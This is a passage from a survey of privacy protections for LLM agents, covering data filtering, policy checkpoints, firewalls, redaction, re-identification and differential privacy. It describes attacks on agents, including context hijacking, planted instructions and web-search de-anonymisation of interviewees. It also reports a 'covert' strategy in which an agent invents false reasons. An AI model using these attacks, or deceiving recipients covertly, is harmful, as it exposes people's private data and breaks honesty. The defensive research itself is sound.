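κ = (observed agreement − chance agreement) / (1 − chance agreement)
```

The annotators marked omissions in 16.5% of responses. Two people marking responses at random at that rate would agree 0.165² + 0.835² ≈ 72% of the time, so the annotators' 75.8% agreement gives a kappa of only 0.12. Kappa for leaks was 0.558, which is usually considered moderate. Omissions were particularly hard to mark because the annotators saw two competing drafts but not the emails and records behind them, so they could hardly notice a detail that both drafts left out.

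Models also disagree with each other. When four models judged leaks in new responses to the same test cases, the average kappa between pairs was 0.47. It rose to 0.71 when the models could read people's comments on other responses to the same request. Such comments can make benchmark scores more reliable, but an agent in a new situation doesn't have them.

*LLM-as-a-Judge for Privacy Evaluation?* (2025) had 677 people and 13 models rate how private 250 texts were. It found that the models accurately approximate people's overall view, but are limited as judges because privacy is so personal. An agent that follows the average view will therefore sometimes share what its own user would have kept private.

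A model's answer may also not show that people disagree about a case. *Measuring Physical-World Privacy Awareness of Large Language Models* (2025) compared models with five human raters on situations in physical settings. The models did well where the raters were unanimous, but they still tended to give similar answers to one another where the raters were divided. The study suggests that the best choice in such cases may be to take no action. An agent that writes emails could ask its user instead.

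Benchmarks often leave out disputed cases. Guo and colleagues had a model play three people, one strict about privacy, one pragmatic and one relaxed, and treated a detail as protected only if all three objected to its disclosure. Requiring agreement makes the labels easier to defend, although agreement among three roles played by one model is weaker evidence than agreement among three people. It also removes many of the cases an assistant would find hardest.

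Mireshghallah argues that contextual privacy, unlike mathematics or programming, has no single correct answer. This is true of many everyday choices, such as how much to tell a manager about a colleague's absence. But some cases do have a clear answer, since hardly anyone would think that a fellow student is entitled to someone's bank details.

### Model judgement or written norms

The case for letting models judge is strongest where no rule applies, because refusing by default also blocks information that people need. Some evidence suggests that models can recognise the relevant norms. In a study by Fu and colleagues, a model's labels matched each of three office workers' judgements on 82.5% to 95% of items, slightly more often than the workers matched each other. But the model had also written those items to be clearly necessary or clearly sensitive.

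Thornton and colleagues argue that models can describe what a document contains but should not decide who receives it. A written policy gives the same answer every time, someone is accountable for it, and an administrator can trace a bad decision to a rule and correct it. Their software made the expected decision on all 2,520 flows under the human-written labels, but this shows only that it applies its policy correctly. It would have scored just as well with a bad policy. The labelling experiment is better evidence for their position because it shows that models can't reliably work out an organisation's decisions from its documents. Larger models or more reasoning did not consistently help.

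That finding doesn't settle what to do when an organisation has made no decision for the model to recover. The tests by Yi and colleagues and by Fu and colleagues are more relevant there, and they show frequent errors in both directions. The strongest evidence against relying on model judgement comes from the court cases, where the most accurate model missed more than half of the violations even though the law was public and each flow came with a description of the case.

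Thornton and colleagues propose a compromise in which a model drafts the descriptive parts of each label and a responsible person approves the list of roles. They have not tested it. Having several records officers label the same documents independently would also help. If their lists differed from each other as much as the models' lists differ from the original, there would be less reason to treat one person's version as the correct norm, though a written policy would still be more consistent than a model.

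## Filtering and coarsening data before the agent sees it

An operator who keeps data away from an agent relies less on the model's judgement about what to share. For example, an agent can't disclose a passport number it never received, however cleverly a stranger asks.

Data is harder to filter from the agent's output than before it reaches the agent. The agent may paraphrase the data, so an output filter has to recognise a diagnosis or a salary in new words. The agent may also have read messages from strangers, and *Firewalls to Secure Dynamic LLM Agentic Networks* (Abdelnabi, Gomaa et al., 2025) argues that any influence those messages had on the agent carries over to an output filter. A filter between the data store and the agent works on the original records, and the operator can keep outsiders' messages away from it. It also protects every later channel, including memory notes and messages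 to other agents, because the agent can't copy data it doesn't have.

One advantage of filtering later is that the recipient is known. Li and Xu (2026), in *ToolMinimize*, found that 81% to 88% of tool calls by three models included private data the tool didn't need. Even when told to protect privacy, the models overshared in 36% to 76% of calls. Li and Xu's software rewrites the inputs of each call just before it goes out, when it can look up what the tool requires. On 307 calls, it cut their measure of exposure by 81% to 92%. A filter in front of the agent has to act before anyone knows which tools the agent will call.

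If a filter removes the sentence about the possible lawsuit from the meeting notes, the agent can't remind its colleagues about the lawsuit. If the filter leaves the sentence in, the agent may still put it in the recap for the outside firm, unless something else tracks where it may go. An operator could split the job into two tasks with different data, but only if they foresee the problem. *Privacy Preference Controls for Agentic Systems* (2026) lists this among the open challenges of data minimisation: how to give an agent minimal privileges when its exact data needs are initially unknown, without burdening the user.

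### Fields, rows and group sizes

Filtering is easiest in a database, where every value sits in a named field. *Reimagining Text-to-SQL* (2026), a survey of models that turn questions into SQL (the standard language for database queries), recommends masking personal identifiers in results, giving agents read-only access and limiting each user to authorised data. The table shows how five common controls could change what an agent gets from a clinic's records:

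| Control | What the agent receives |
|---|---|
| Field removal | Names and appointment times, without the "reason for visit" field |
| Masking | A phone number with all but the last three digits hidden |
| Row filter | Tomorrow's appointments only |
| Purpose-bound view | Names, numbers and times for patients who agreed to reminders |
| Minimum group size | Patient counts by diagnosis, without any diagnosis that has fewer than three patients |

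A view is a stored query that behaves like a table. A purpose-bound view removes fields and filters rows, much as the Hippocratic database returned only the records of customers who had accepted book recommendations. It can also reduce the problem of agents declaring false purposes. If the operator gives a reminder agent access only to the reminder view, the agent doesn't have to declare a purpose, so it can't claim to be doing the billing.

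Minimum group sizes protect people in statistics, because a count or average for one person is that person's data. *Please Don't Kill My Vibe* (Summers, Mohammed and Wu, 2025) cites a US federal committee's minimum of three for public reports. It also describes how US education law requires schools to report test scores separately by ethnicity, disability and other characteristics, so that an overall average can't hide a struggling group. The two rules conflict when finer splits produce groups below the minimum size, which are then removed from the report. Somebody has to decide in advance which rule takes priority.

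### Rewriting the query

Access rules determine which records a query may read, but not how it may combine them. A hospital might let a physician see customer profiles and health records separately, but forbid joining the two without the patient's consent. *Please Don't Kill My Vibe* proposed that databases enforce such rules themselves, and Summers and Wu (2026) developed the idea in *Data Flow Control*. An administrator writes a policy about which input records may contribute to each row of a result. Software then adds the policy to every query that uses those records before the database runs the query.

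Their running example is an agent that prepares tax reports from a table of receipts. Suppose one policy says that any result must combine receipts from at least three people, and the agent asks for total spending by category. In simplified form:

```
Policy:           SOURCE Receipts
                  CONSTRAINT COUNT(DISTINCT Receipts.uid) > 2
                  ON FAIL REMOVE

Agent's query:    SELECT cat, SUM(cost)
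                  FROM Receipts
                  GROUP BY cat

Rewritten query:  SELECT cat, SUM(cost)
                  FROM Receipts
                  GROUP BY cat
                  HAVING COUNT(DISTINCT uid) > 2
```

Here *uid* identifies the person and *cat* the category. The added line counts the people whose receipts make up each total and drops any total with too few people. If nine people have receipts for meals but only one has a medical receipt, the agent gets the meals total but not the medical one. If the agent asks for the raw receipts instead, each row comes from one person, so the policy removes every row. No model helps enforce the rule, so the agent can't persuade one to make an exception.

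Policies can also refer to other tables and to how the data is used. The paper's privacy policy exempts administrators by looking up the current user's role, and another policy stops the agent from deducting more than 50% of a meal's cost. When a result breaks a policy, the administrator can have the database remove the row, cancel the query or call a function that repairs the result.

Summers and Wu mainly tested speed. On standard analytics queries in five database systems, the rewritten queries took about as long as the originals on average. Recording the origin of every result row and checking it afterwards made some queries at least 20 times slower. In a separate test, they ran 1,000 updates, 30% of which broke a rule about the order in which a record may change status. Their software and GPT-5.2 both caught every violation, but the software was about a hundred times faster. The method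 covers only one query at a time, so someone may still be able to work out one person's spending by subtracting one permitted total from another. It also leaves out some kinds of query, such as recursive ones.

*Environment Steering* (Summers, Raghunath and colleagues, 2026) extends the method to tool calls. Its system records the user's request, every tool call and every result as rows in tables, and checks each new call as if the agent were inserting a row. For example, a policy can allow a Social Security number in the final answer only if it belongs to the patient the user asked about. On four benchmarks, the success rate of attacks and leaks, averaged across five open models, fell from 30–74% to 0.2–14%.

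The share of tasks an agent completes depends heavily on how the software responds after blocking a call. On AgentDyn, a benchmark of everyday tasks with planted instructions, ending the task at the first violation lowered this share by 36.2 percentage points, while returning a generic error message lowered it by 10.5 points. When the message named the broken rule and the data the agent could use instead, the share was 6.5 points higher than with no protection. Attacks almost never succeeded in any of the three versions. The policies fitted their tasks unusually well because a model wrote them for each task and the researchers checked them against the benchmark's requirements. Even so, some of the policies for Kimi K2.5 were too strict and blocked safe actions.

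### Narrowing the owner's grant

Many agents work through services such as bug trackers and never write a database query. They often borrow a credential that gives much more access than the task needs. An agent that summarises issues from one engineering project may hold a credential for every project. *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (Millstone, Akidau and colleagues, 2026), from the data company Redpanda, presents Out-of-Band Policy Enforcement (OBPE), which routes every call and result through a checkpoint between the agent and the service. The checkpoint can refuse a call, hold it for approval or narrow it. It can then drop records, strip fields and mask text in the result before the model reads it.

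Two policies apply to each call. The data's owner sets the most that any agent may receive or change. Whoever builds a particular agent can add a policy for that agent, and the checkpoint combines the two:

```
decision = the stricter of the two   (deny < hold for approval < permit)
records  = owner's filter AND agent's filter
limit    = the smaller of the two limits
fields   = fields that both policies allow
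```

Suppose the owner lets agents list issues with their title, status and priority. The builder's policy asks for the title, the status and the reporter's email address, for one team's issues, up to 100 at a time. The agent then receives only the titles and statuses of that team's issues. It doesn't get the email address, because the builder's policy, however it is worded, can't grant access that the owner's policy doesn't. Millstone and colleagues prove this property, provided that all calls go through the checkpoint and the platform identifies the agent by some means the agent can't alter. If the owner's policy grants too much, the checkpoint will still enforce it as written.

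They tested OBPE on 71 tasks with four models and simulated versions of Jira (a tracker for software work) and ServiceNow (a system for IT requests). Including comparisons between versions of the checkpoint, there were 3,621 trials. A trial counted as a failure if protected data reached the model, if an exact protected value appeared in the answer or if the agent completed a forbidden change:

| Outcome | No protection | Six written rules in the prompt | Rules and OBPE |
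|---|---|---|---|
| Any failure | 63.3% | 57.6% | 0.2% |
| Protected data reached the model | 55.1% | 52.1% | 0.0% |
| Exact protected value in the answer | 27.5% | 3.7% | 0.2% |
| Forbidden change completed | 8.1% | 5.5% | 0.0% |
| Requested job done | 83.2% | 79.1% | 60.9% |
| Allowed work done without a failure or disclosure | 19.1% | 22.0% | 58.9% |

The written rules made the agents more discreet in their answers but barely changed what they read. Most of the fall from 57.6% to 0.2% therefore comes from data that reached the model without appearing in its answer. Whether that is harmful depends on what the agent does next, since it may put the data in a later email. The reduction was 41.2 percentage points when Millstone and colleagues gave related tasks less weight so that no group of similar scenarios dominated.

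The drop in completed jobs doesn't measure over-blocking in ordinary work. The policies were meant to deny ten of the 71 tasks and hold two for approval, but the scoring still counted those as jobs to complete. Only five tasks were supposed to pass unchanged. On the other 54 tasks, where OBPE was meant to alter the request or the result, agents completed the job 71.7% of the time.

The study also compared OBPE with a second model that reviewed the agent's messages. With Claude Sonnet 4.6, the agent failed in 58.6% of trials with the reviewer and in none with OBPE. This comparison favours OBPE by design, because a reviewer of messages can't stop data from reaching the model. Job completion rates are more informative. The agent completed 58.7% of jobs with the reviewer and 66.2% with OBPE. The reviewer sometimes replaced a useful answer with a refusal, and it needed 930 extra model calls.

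Refusing calls and filtering records, with no other control, prevented failures in 46.7% of trials with Sonnet. Stripping fields raised this to 69.4%. Masking whole fields and restricting what the agent could write raised it to 88.6%, and searching the remaining text for patterns such as passwords raised it to 100%. Millstone and colleagues don't expect the 100% figure to hold elsewhere, because pattern matching can always miss a secret in an unfamiliar format.

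A few disclosures still occurred after the checkpoint removed fields. In four answers, the agent gave an exact email address it had never received, which it worked out from the person's name and the company's usual address format. In another trial, the checkpoint hid the email addresses but still let the agent search on them, and the agent reported how many records matched. It found two matches for "@partner", then one each for "yara" and "singh". Preventing this would require restricting the agent's searches or blurring the counts, and the test included neither.

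Field-level controls also need tool output with defined fields. Millstone and colleagues cite a survey of 1,856 tools on 100 popular Model Context Protocol servers, in which only 234 declared the structure of their output. For the rest, somebody has to describe the output before a policy can refer to any part of it, and keep the description up to date.

### Choosing the data before the conversation starts

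A personal assistant faces too many kinds of request for anyone to write a policy for each. In *AirGapAgent*, Bagdasarian, Yi and colleagues at Google (2024) proposed letting a model choose which data the agent sees. They were concerned about agents that talk to outside parties, such as a restaurant's booking system. The researchers use the term "context hijacking" for an attack in which an outside party misleads the agent about the situation. In one example, the restaurant's side claims that aliens have invaded and demand the user's age, and some models revealed it in response.

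AirGapAgent divides the work between two models. Before the conversation, a "minimiser" reads the user's task, a general privacy instruction and the user's data, and picks out the fields the task needs. A second model talks to the outsider and receives only those fields. Nothing the outsider writes reaches the minimiser, so even a convincing lie can extract only what the minimiser has already released. If the outsider legitimately needs something else, as when a doctor's office asks about exercise habits, the agent can ask the user to approve sharing it.

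The test used 20 invented people with up to 26 fields each and eight situations, such as booking a table or preparing for a doctor's appointment. In the table, the first number in each pair is for an outsider that asked plainly and the second for one that tried to mislead the agent. These are results for the easier fields and situations, with multiple-choice answers:

| Model and design | Appropriate data shared | Private data withheld |
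|---|---|---|
| Gemini Ultra, one model | 98.9% / 98.2% | 94.4% / 45.2% |
| Gemini Ultra, AirGapAgent | 88.7% / 87.3% | 97.2% / 96.7% |
| GPT-4, one model | 79.6% / 100.0% | 93.8% / 31.4% |
| GPT-4, AirGapAgent | 78.9% / 88.9% | 97.0% / 86.8% |

A single model protected data well until somebody lied to it. With AirGapAgent, the lies had almost no effect on Gemini Ultra and some effect on GPT-4. However, the minimiser wrongly withheld about a tenth of the information that Gemini Ultra should have shared. Gemini Ultra's scores are also probably inflated, because it generated the labels that defined the right answers.

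The minimiser needs a precise description of the task. When Bagdasarian and colleagues gave it only the general area, such as "recommend" instead of "recommend a movie for tonight", the share of private data that the agent withheld from a plain-spoken outsider fell from 96.8% to 68.6%. Removing a field also didn't always hide the information. In open-ended conversations with a misleading outsider, the minimiser removed the user's gender in 73% of the cases where it was private, but the agent withheld it in only 39%. An agent can often guess gender from a name or an email address.

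The design suits a profile in which each fact has its own field, but much of what an assistant reads mixes facts together. *ConVerse* (Gomaa, Salem and Abdelnabi, 2025) gives the example of an email from a woman to her partner about buying a home. The email says they need two or three bedrooms, which an estate agent should know, but it also mentions a fertility appointment and her father's promotion. A filter that can only pass or block the whole email will either disclose the appointment or withhold the number of bedrooms.

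### Two firewalls around an assistant

ConVerse is a benchmark for assistants that negotiate with another company's agent. It has 12 invented users and covers travel, real estate and insurance. In 611 privacy attacks, the outside agent asks for personal information and gives a plausible reason. In 253 security attacks, it tries to make the assistant do something the user wouldn't want, such as cancel an appointment or buy an expensive extra. Gomaa and colleagues sort personal data into data that is unrelated to the task, related but private, or useful but only to be shared in less detail. In the third group, "Lisa's parents visit monthly from Vancouver" should become "needs guest accommodation for family visits". Privacy attacks on seven unprotected models succeeded 37% to 88% of the time.

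Abdelnabi and colleagues designed two "firewalls" for this setting. One controls what the outside agent can say to the assistant, and the other controls how much detail the assistant gets about its user.

Incoming messages go through the Language Converter Firewall, in three steps:

1. A model turns the message into a form with fixed fields, such as room type, price per night and dates.
2. Ordinary software checks every field and deletes anything the form doesn't allow. A room type must come from a list, and a price must be a number.
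3. The software replaces names, which no list could cover, with codes. A hotel whose name is really a planted instruction, for example, reaches the assistant as "hotel_3".

An attacker might fool the model in the first step, but the output still has to pass the software's check. The form has no field for flattery, urgency or instructions, so these never reach the assistant.

The Data Abstraction Firewall sits between the assistant and the user's files. When the assistant looks something up, the raw data goes first to the firewall, where a model rewrites it according to written rules. A home address becomes "departing from the Paris area" and an exact age becomes "adult". The model removes other details, such as government identity numbers. It receives the data and the rules, but not the assistant's query or the conversation with the outside agent.

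Claude Sonnet 4 wrote the rules for both firewalls from example conversations involving two of the four users in each domain. To design the form, it read only honest conversations, because attackers' questions might have led it to add fields such as a full medical history. To write the abstraction rules, it read both honest conversations and attacks. Abdelnabi and colleagues expected rules based only on honest conversations to be too permissive, because models tend to overshare in those conversations, and rules based only on attacks to block too much. The abstraction rules were 54 lines long for insurance, 109 for travel and 203 for real estate.

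They tested each firewall separately on travel planning with GPT-5:

| Protection | Privacy attacks that succeeded | Security attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| None | 88.5% | 55.3% |
| Data abstraction only | 29.3% | 30.8% |
| Language conversion only | 20.7% | 1.1% |
| Both | 7.8% | 3.3% |

A model that judged the assistant's travel plans rated them slightly higher with both firewalls than with none, perhaps because the assistant had less irrelevant material to read. Privacy attacks succeeded in 9.1% of cases for users whose conversations were not used to make the rules, compared with 6.4% for users whose conversations were. Across all three domains, these attacks succeeded against both firewalls in 10.2% of cases with GPT-5 and 16.8% with Claude Sonnet 4.

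Converting the incoming messages into form fields protected privacy at least as well as coarsening the data. If the outside agent asks for prescription details as part of a "medical compatibility check", the form has no field for that request, so the assistant never sees it. But this works only where a form can hold everything the two sides need to discuss. Abdelnabi and colleagues acknowledge that it suits travel or insurance better than open-ended collaboration, where more fields would contain free text and replacing that text with codes could make the assistant less useful.

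### Coarsening compared with blocking

Abdelnabi and colleagues also adapted AirGapAgent to the benchmark, to test whether coarsening data works better than passing or blocking it. A model first classified each item as relevant or irrelevant to travel planning, and the assistant received the relevant items in full and the others not at all. Privacy attacks succeeded in 67.3% of cases with this filter and in 5.5% with the two firewalls. The filter did worst on data that was useful to the task, because it classified such data as relevant and released every detail. Attacks on that data succeeded in 76.2% of cases, compared with 23.8% for the firewalls.

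The comparison exaggerates the benefit of coarsening. The firewalls also had the language converter, which the binary filter lacked, and the test covered only the two users whose conversations had shaped the rules. The result for abstraction alone, 29.3% over all four users, is a better guide and still far below 67.3%. The binary filter also allowed 64.6% of attacks on data unrelated to the task, which it should have been able to block. The task description it received was broad, covering activities, restaurants, preferences and insurance. AirGapAgent's tests had shown that broad descriptions weaken the minimiser.

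The researchers examined every attack that got past both firewalls. In nearly all the privacy failures, either the assistant shared the right kind of information in too much detail or a permitted field contained more than its name suggested. For instance, the assistant mentioned "rock climbing and scuba diving" where "high-risk adventure activities" would have been enough. An insurance rule allowed "recent claim history", but those records listed particular equipment and amounts. No attacker defeated the software check or reached the abstraction model in any of these failures.

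About three quarters of the security failures involved offers that the user didn't need, such as an insurance add-on. These offers fitted the form, so only the assistant could have judged whether the user wanted them. In the rest, the assistant made the mistake without any outside influence. For example, when one user asked it to tell a manager about some days of absence, it also emailed the manager the holiday details.

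The two firewalls offer different kinds of protection. Software checks the converter's output, but a model performs the abstraction and nothing checks its work. Outsiders can't manipulate that model during the conversation because it doesn't receive their messages, but it can still make ordinary errors or follow instructions planted in the user's own files. Abdelnabi and colleagues assume that those files are trustworthy, which is a large assumption for a mailbox, since anyone can send an email. Coarse details such as a region, a rare allergy and the children's ages may also identify a person when put together, and the abstraction firewall doesn't check for this.

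The abstraction rules are also fixed for each domain, regardless of the current request. The travel rules block passport details, which is right while the assistant is comparing hotels but wrong when it has to book an international flight. In terms of contextual integrity, the rules depend on the type of information and the general setting, but not on whether the recipient is an airline or a tour operator, or whether the assistant is planning or booking. The assistant can't get the passport number by explaining why it needs it, because the firewall never receives the explanation. This makes the firewall hard to manipulate, but it also means that the user has to supply the number directly or somebody has to change the rule.

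## Redacting, summarising and paraphrasing text

The data abstraction firewall relies on a model to rewrite free text. Besides making details less specific, an agent can redact parts of the text, replace names with pseudonyms, summarise or paraphrase. Lahjouji and Colaco point out that every such change involves a trade-off with usefulness, so it matters which facts each operation loses and which it keeps.

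### One message, two recipients

Suppose a payroll manager sends this message to her department:

> Priya Nair (52, payroll, Leeds) starts chemotherapy next week and will be out every Tuesday until 30 June. Tom Reed will cover for her.

An agent has to pass the news on to two outsiders. An accountant needs to know whom to call on Tuesdays, but not why Priya is away. A consultant who studies sick leave needs the reason and the pattern of absence, but not the person. The agent could try each operation for each of them:

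| Operation | For the accountant | For the consultant |
|---|---|---|
| Redaction | Priya Nair ([removed]) starts [removed] next week and will be out every Tuesday until 30 June. Tom Reed will cover for her. | [Name] (52, payroll, [place]) starts chemotherapy next week and will be out every Tuesday until [date]. [Name] will cover for her. |
| Consistent pseudonyms | Unsuitable, because the accountant needs the real names | Employee A (52, payroll, Leeds) starts chemotherapy next week and will be out every Tuesday until 30 June. Employee B will cover for her. |
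| Generalisation | Priya Nair has a regular commitment and will be out every Tuesday until 30 June. Tom Reed will cover for her. | An employee in her fifties is starting medical treatment and will be out one day a week until the summer. |
| Summary | On Tuesdays until 30 June, contact Tom Reed instead of Priya Nair. | One employee will miss a day a week for chemotherapy until the end of June. |
| Paraphrase | Tom Reed will stand in for Priya Nair on Tuesdays until the end of June while she has cancer treatment. | A 52-year-old in the Leeds payroll office is having chemotherapy and will be away on Tuesdays until July. |

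The summaries work best here because each contains only what its reader needs. The paraphrases change the wording but don't protect anyone, because the accountant still learns about the cancer and the consultant could still find Priya on a staff list.

### What each operation changes

Redaction software usually relies on named-entity recognition, in which a model labels the names, places and dates in a text. Many tools also search for text that fits a set pattern, such as card numbers. The software replaces each item it finds with a mask and leaves the rest of the text unchanged. An operator can check the result by searching it for known names and numbers, but this misses those in unexpected forms, such as a phone number with "euhm" in the middle.

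To use consistent pseudonyms, software must also recognise that "Priya", "Ms Nair" and "she" refer to the same person, and give her the same substitute each time. Readers can still follow who is covering for whom. *LLMs as Linguistic Chameleons* (2026) describes methods that keep the list of replacements and reverse them later, so an agent could send disguised text to an outside service and restore the names in the answer. The operator has to check that no original name remains and that the recipient can't get the list. However, a consistent pseudonym links everything written about Employee A into one profile, and EU law still treats pseudonymised data as personal data.

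Generalisation replaces a value with a wider category, for example, an exact age with an age range. Software can check that 52 lies between 50 and 59 and count how many employees are in that range, but it can't so easily check whether "a regular commitment" is a fair description of chemotherapy.

When a model summarises, it chooses what to keep instead of marking what to remove, so the summary doesn't show what was left out. *How Private are Language Models in Abstractive Summarization?* (Hughes, Ma and Aletras, 2024) tested six models, all now outdated, on hospital records and refugee cases with invented personal details added. Summarising first and then removing personal details from the summary protected privacy particularly well. Two doctors who wrote summaries for comparison revealed only gender, through pronouns, at a rate of 4%. GPT-4o's rates were 8% for gender and 12.4% for location.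 The automatic checkers missed pronouns. One model listed the details it had removed, including the person's age and first name.

Paraphrasing rewrites sentences and is meant to preserve their content. It removes distinctive wording that somebody might recognise or search for, but leaves the facts in place. Checking a paraphrase or summary therefore means testing both whether each statement agrees with the original and whether a second model can still infer the protected facts.

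### Why removing names does not remove identity

The pseudonymised message still describes a 52-year-old who works in payroll in Leeds. Suppose the company has 1,000 employees, of whom 1 in 20 work in payroll, 1 in 10 work in Leeds and 1 in 25 are 52 years old. If these traits are independent, the expected number of employees with all three is:

```
1,000 × 1/20 × 1/10 × 1/25 = 0.2
```

Priya has all three traits, so whether they identify her depends on how many of her 999 colleagues share them. The expected number is again about 0.2, and the chance that no colleague shares all three is (1 − 1/5,000)^999, or about 82%. A summary that keeps all three traits would therefore probably identify her to anyone with a staff list.

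If 1 in 5 employees are in their fifties, generalising Priya's age to "fifties" reduces the chance that she is the only match to 37%. About one colleague is then expected to match, and leaving out Leeds as well raises that number to about ten.

Real traits are rarely independent. If the whole payroll team works in Leeds, mentioning Leeds reveals nothing new about a payroll employee, and about two colleagues would match the original description. If Priya is the only payroll employee in Leeds, those two traits identify her even without her age.

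Krčo, Yao and colleagues (2026), in *RAT-Bench*, used US census data to take such connections into account. They generated medical consultations, chatbot conversations and meeting transcripts about invented people with unusual combinations of traits, and ran 12 anonymisation tools on them. GPT-4.1 then tried to recover the details. A person counted as re-identified if it recovered a direct identifier, such as a phone number, or a combination of traits that fewer than five people in the US were likely to share. The table gives the share of people re-identified, depending on how the text expressed the details:

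| Tool | Standard form | Unusual form | Only implied |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 98% | 32% |
| Presidio (Microsoft's open-source tool) | 41% | 77% | 30% |
| Azure (Microsoft's cloud service) | 22% | 33% | 21% |
| GPT-4.1 with a redaction prompt | 26% | 58% | 19% |
| Average of all 12 tools | 44% | 69% | 28% |

The tools removed most direct identifiers when details appeared in standard form, and the remaining risk came mainly from combinations of other traits. Most tools made little difference when the text only implied the details. Azure's low rates came partly from also deleting harmless words. In a separate test on 50 of the texts, a prompt asking for a summary of at most two sentences, without names, cut re-identification to 4% or less. But such a summary gives only the topic and the person's general question, which is too little for many tasks.

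An attacker with web access can identify people in redacted text without a staff list. Wen and Li (2026), in *AgentDoxx*, generated 822 interviews based on public information about real people who had identified themselves on Reddit. They removed direct identifiers and told models to name the interviewee, using up to ten web searches. The five best setups succeeded in 47% to 48% of cases. Three open models named the right person in 15% to 28% of cases without searching, so blocking web access would not be enough to prevent identification. With the six strongest setups, 89% to 97% of the guesses that the model marked as high-confidence were correct, so an attacker would know which guesses to trust.

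Wen and Li then tested defences on 143 interviews, all of which at least one setup had already identified:

| Change to the text | Average success across 12 setups |
|---|---|
| None | 75.1% |
| Named entities masked | 62.0% |
| Named entities masked, then text paraphrased | 45.9% |
| Passages removed that a trained model marked as identifying | 35.1% |
| Identifying details replaced with false ones | 34.2% |

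After masking, at least one setup still identified 85.3% of the interviewees. Ordinary phrasing, such as a job description together with a project and a period of time, revealed who they were. False details worked better on average, but several models dismissed the contradictions as transcription errors. False details can also harm a stranger. In the main experiment, when the right person appeared in the search results but the model chose a different answer, it usually named a specific wrong person.

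These people had public profiles that matched their interviews, so the rates are much higher than for ordinary text. Wen and Li found matches they could verify for 43 (3.4%) of the 1,250 real interviews that Anthropic anonymised and published.

### Using an attacker to guide the rewriting

An anonymiser can use a model's guesses about a person to decide what to change in a text. In a method that Staab and colleagues published in 2025, one model infers personal attributes from a text, another rewrites the text to hide them, and these steps repeat. Krčo and colleagues found that this method reduced re-identification to 2% for details in standard form when they gave it the complete list of 15 attributes to hide. When they gave it only five, chosen at random, the rate was 44%, no better than the average of the simpler tools.

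Li, Wen and Li (2026), in *LLM Anonymization Against Agentic Re-Identification*, therefore had a model draw up a list for each text. Their system, AURA, works in four steps:

1. A model with web search looks for details that could identify this particular person and adds them to eight standard attributes, such as age and occupation.
2. A model infers those attributes and rewrites the text to hide them, for several rounds if necessary. Comparing the result with the original shows which passages need to change.
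3. A model writes several alternative replacements for those passages only.
4. One model scores what each version still reveals and another scores what useful content it has lost. AURA rejects versions that are too specific, if it has an alternative, and chooses the one that reveals least. It considers lost content only to break ties.

They tested AURA on 53 of the real Anthropic interviews, which a searching agent had previously linked to particular people. Three models then tried to identify the interviewees again. The last column gives the share of links between an interviewee's background and views that a model could still recover:

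| Method | Re-identified, of 53 | Links recovered |
|---|---|---|
| Presidio | 26–40 | 95.6% |
| One rewrite, short prompt | 11–18 | 87.0% |
| One rewrite, detailed prompt | 23–33 | 96.5% |
| Method of Staab and colleagues | 10–12 | 66.3% |
| AURA | 0–7 | 72.0–76.1% |

Most of AURA's privacy advantage comes from its longer list of attributes. When it used only the eight standard attributes and the same underlying model as the older method, the two protected people about equally well. The detailed prompt hid identities less well than the short one, perhaps because it also included instructions on what to preserve.

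Human raters judged 86.9% of a sample of AURA's rewrites faithful to the original. AURA offers no guarantee against a stronger attacker. An agent that used it on private email would disclose identifying details to the search provider, because AURA searches the web for them.

### What differential privacy guarantees for text

Differential privacy does offer a guarantee, and it holds whatever else the reader knows. It requires a rewriting method *M* that makes random choices. For any two possible messages *x* and *y*, and any output *z*:

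```
Pr[M(x) = z]  ≤  e^ε · Pr[M(y) = z] + δ
```

The parameter ε sets the strength of the protection, and δ is a small allowance for failure. If δ is zero and ε is 0.1, no output is more than about 1.1 times as likely to come from one message as from another, so a reader learns almost nothing about which message produced it. If ε is 10, the output can be up to about 22,000 times as likely.

Strong protection conflicts with the purpose of a message. "The loan is approved" and "the loan is refused" must produce any given output with nearly the same probability, so the recipient can't tell which one the sender wrote. Weaker settings can also destroy meaning. *Beyond Theoretical Bounds* (Li, Grivet Sébert and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a request for "flights from indianapolis to seattle washington", which one method turned into "moving from india to salt washing". In the test of AURA,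 a differentially private method with ε set to 10 prevented every re-identification, but none of the links between background and views could be recovered. At the weaker setting of ε = 140, 59.3% of the links could be recovered, but attackers identified 4 to 10 of the 53 people.

A value of ε means little unless the reader knows what unit it protects. *Spend Your Budget Wisely* (2025) stresses that a method must state whether its guarantee covers a word or a whole document. Under the basic rule for adding guarantees, rewriting 20 words with an ε of 10 each gives an ε of 200 for the sentence. *On the Impact of Noise in Differentially Private Text Rewriting* (2025) reports that document-level methods need very high values, such as 1,000, to produce meaningful text. At that level, the formal limit hardly restricts anything.

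Li, Grivet Sébert and colleagues also measured protection directly, by having an attacker choose which of two texts a rewrite came from. With two methods that protect whole sentences, the attacker did little better than chance even at an ε of 1,000, but the rewrites often had nothing to do with the original. Methods that protect single words kept more of the meaning but gave the attacker much more information about the source text. Differential privacy is therefore better suited to finding patterns in many documents than to sending someone a particular message.

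### Information sufficiency

The experiments on anonymisation measure what a reader can find out about a person, but an agent that answers email also has to give the reader enough to act on. In *Say Something Else*, Xiao, Li and colleagues (2026) define this task, which they call information sufficiency, as drafting a reply that achieves the user's goal while revealing as little private information as possible. They judge replies by privacy, usefulness and "covertness", which means that the reader doesn't notice the agent is managing information.

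In their example, a user needs time off for a job interview and asks the agent to write to her manager. They compare three strategies:

- **Suppression:** the agent asks for the time off without giving a reason.
- **Generalisation:** it gives a true but vague reason, such as a personal appointment.
- **Pseudonymisation:** it gives a false but plausible reason, such as a training session.

The last strategy goes well beyond replacing a name with "Employee A", because the reader doesn't know that the agent has replaced anything.

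They adapted PrivacyLens into 792 scenarios in which somebody asks about the user's private affairs. Seven models replied under each strategy and with no protection, which produced 22,176 conversations. After the first reply, a model playing the recipient wrote two follow-up messages, which the agent answered. Another model then read the conversation and guessed the private details. An exact guess counted as 1 and the right general category as 0.5. The combined score is (1 − leakage) × usefulness, calculated for each conversation and then averaged:

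| Strategy | Exact guesses after first reply | Exact guesses after follow-up | Leakage | Usefulness | Combined |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| No protection | 27.4% | 33.6% | 0.294 | 0.952 | 0.694 |
| Suppression | 9.6% | 17.9% | 0.165 | 0.824 | 0.730 |
| Generalisation | 13.7% | 25.5% | 0.237 | 0.806 | 0.664 |
| Pseudonymisation | 15.2% | 19.1% | 0.216 | 0.938 | 0.764 |

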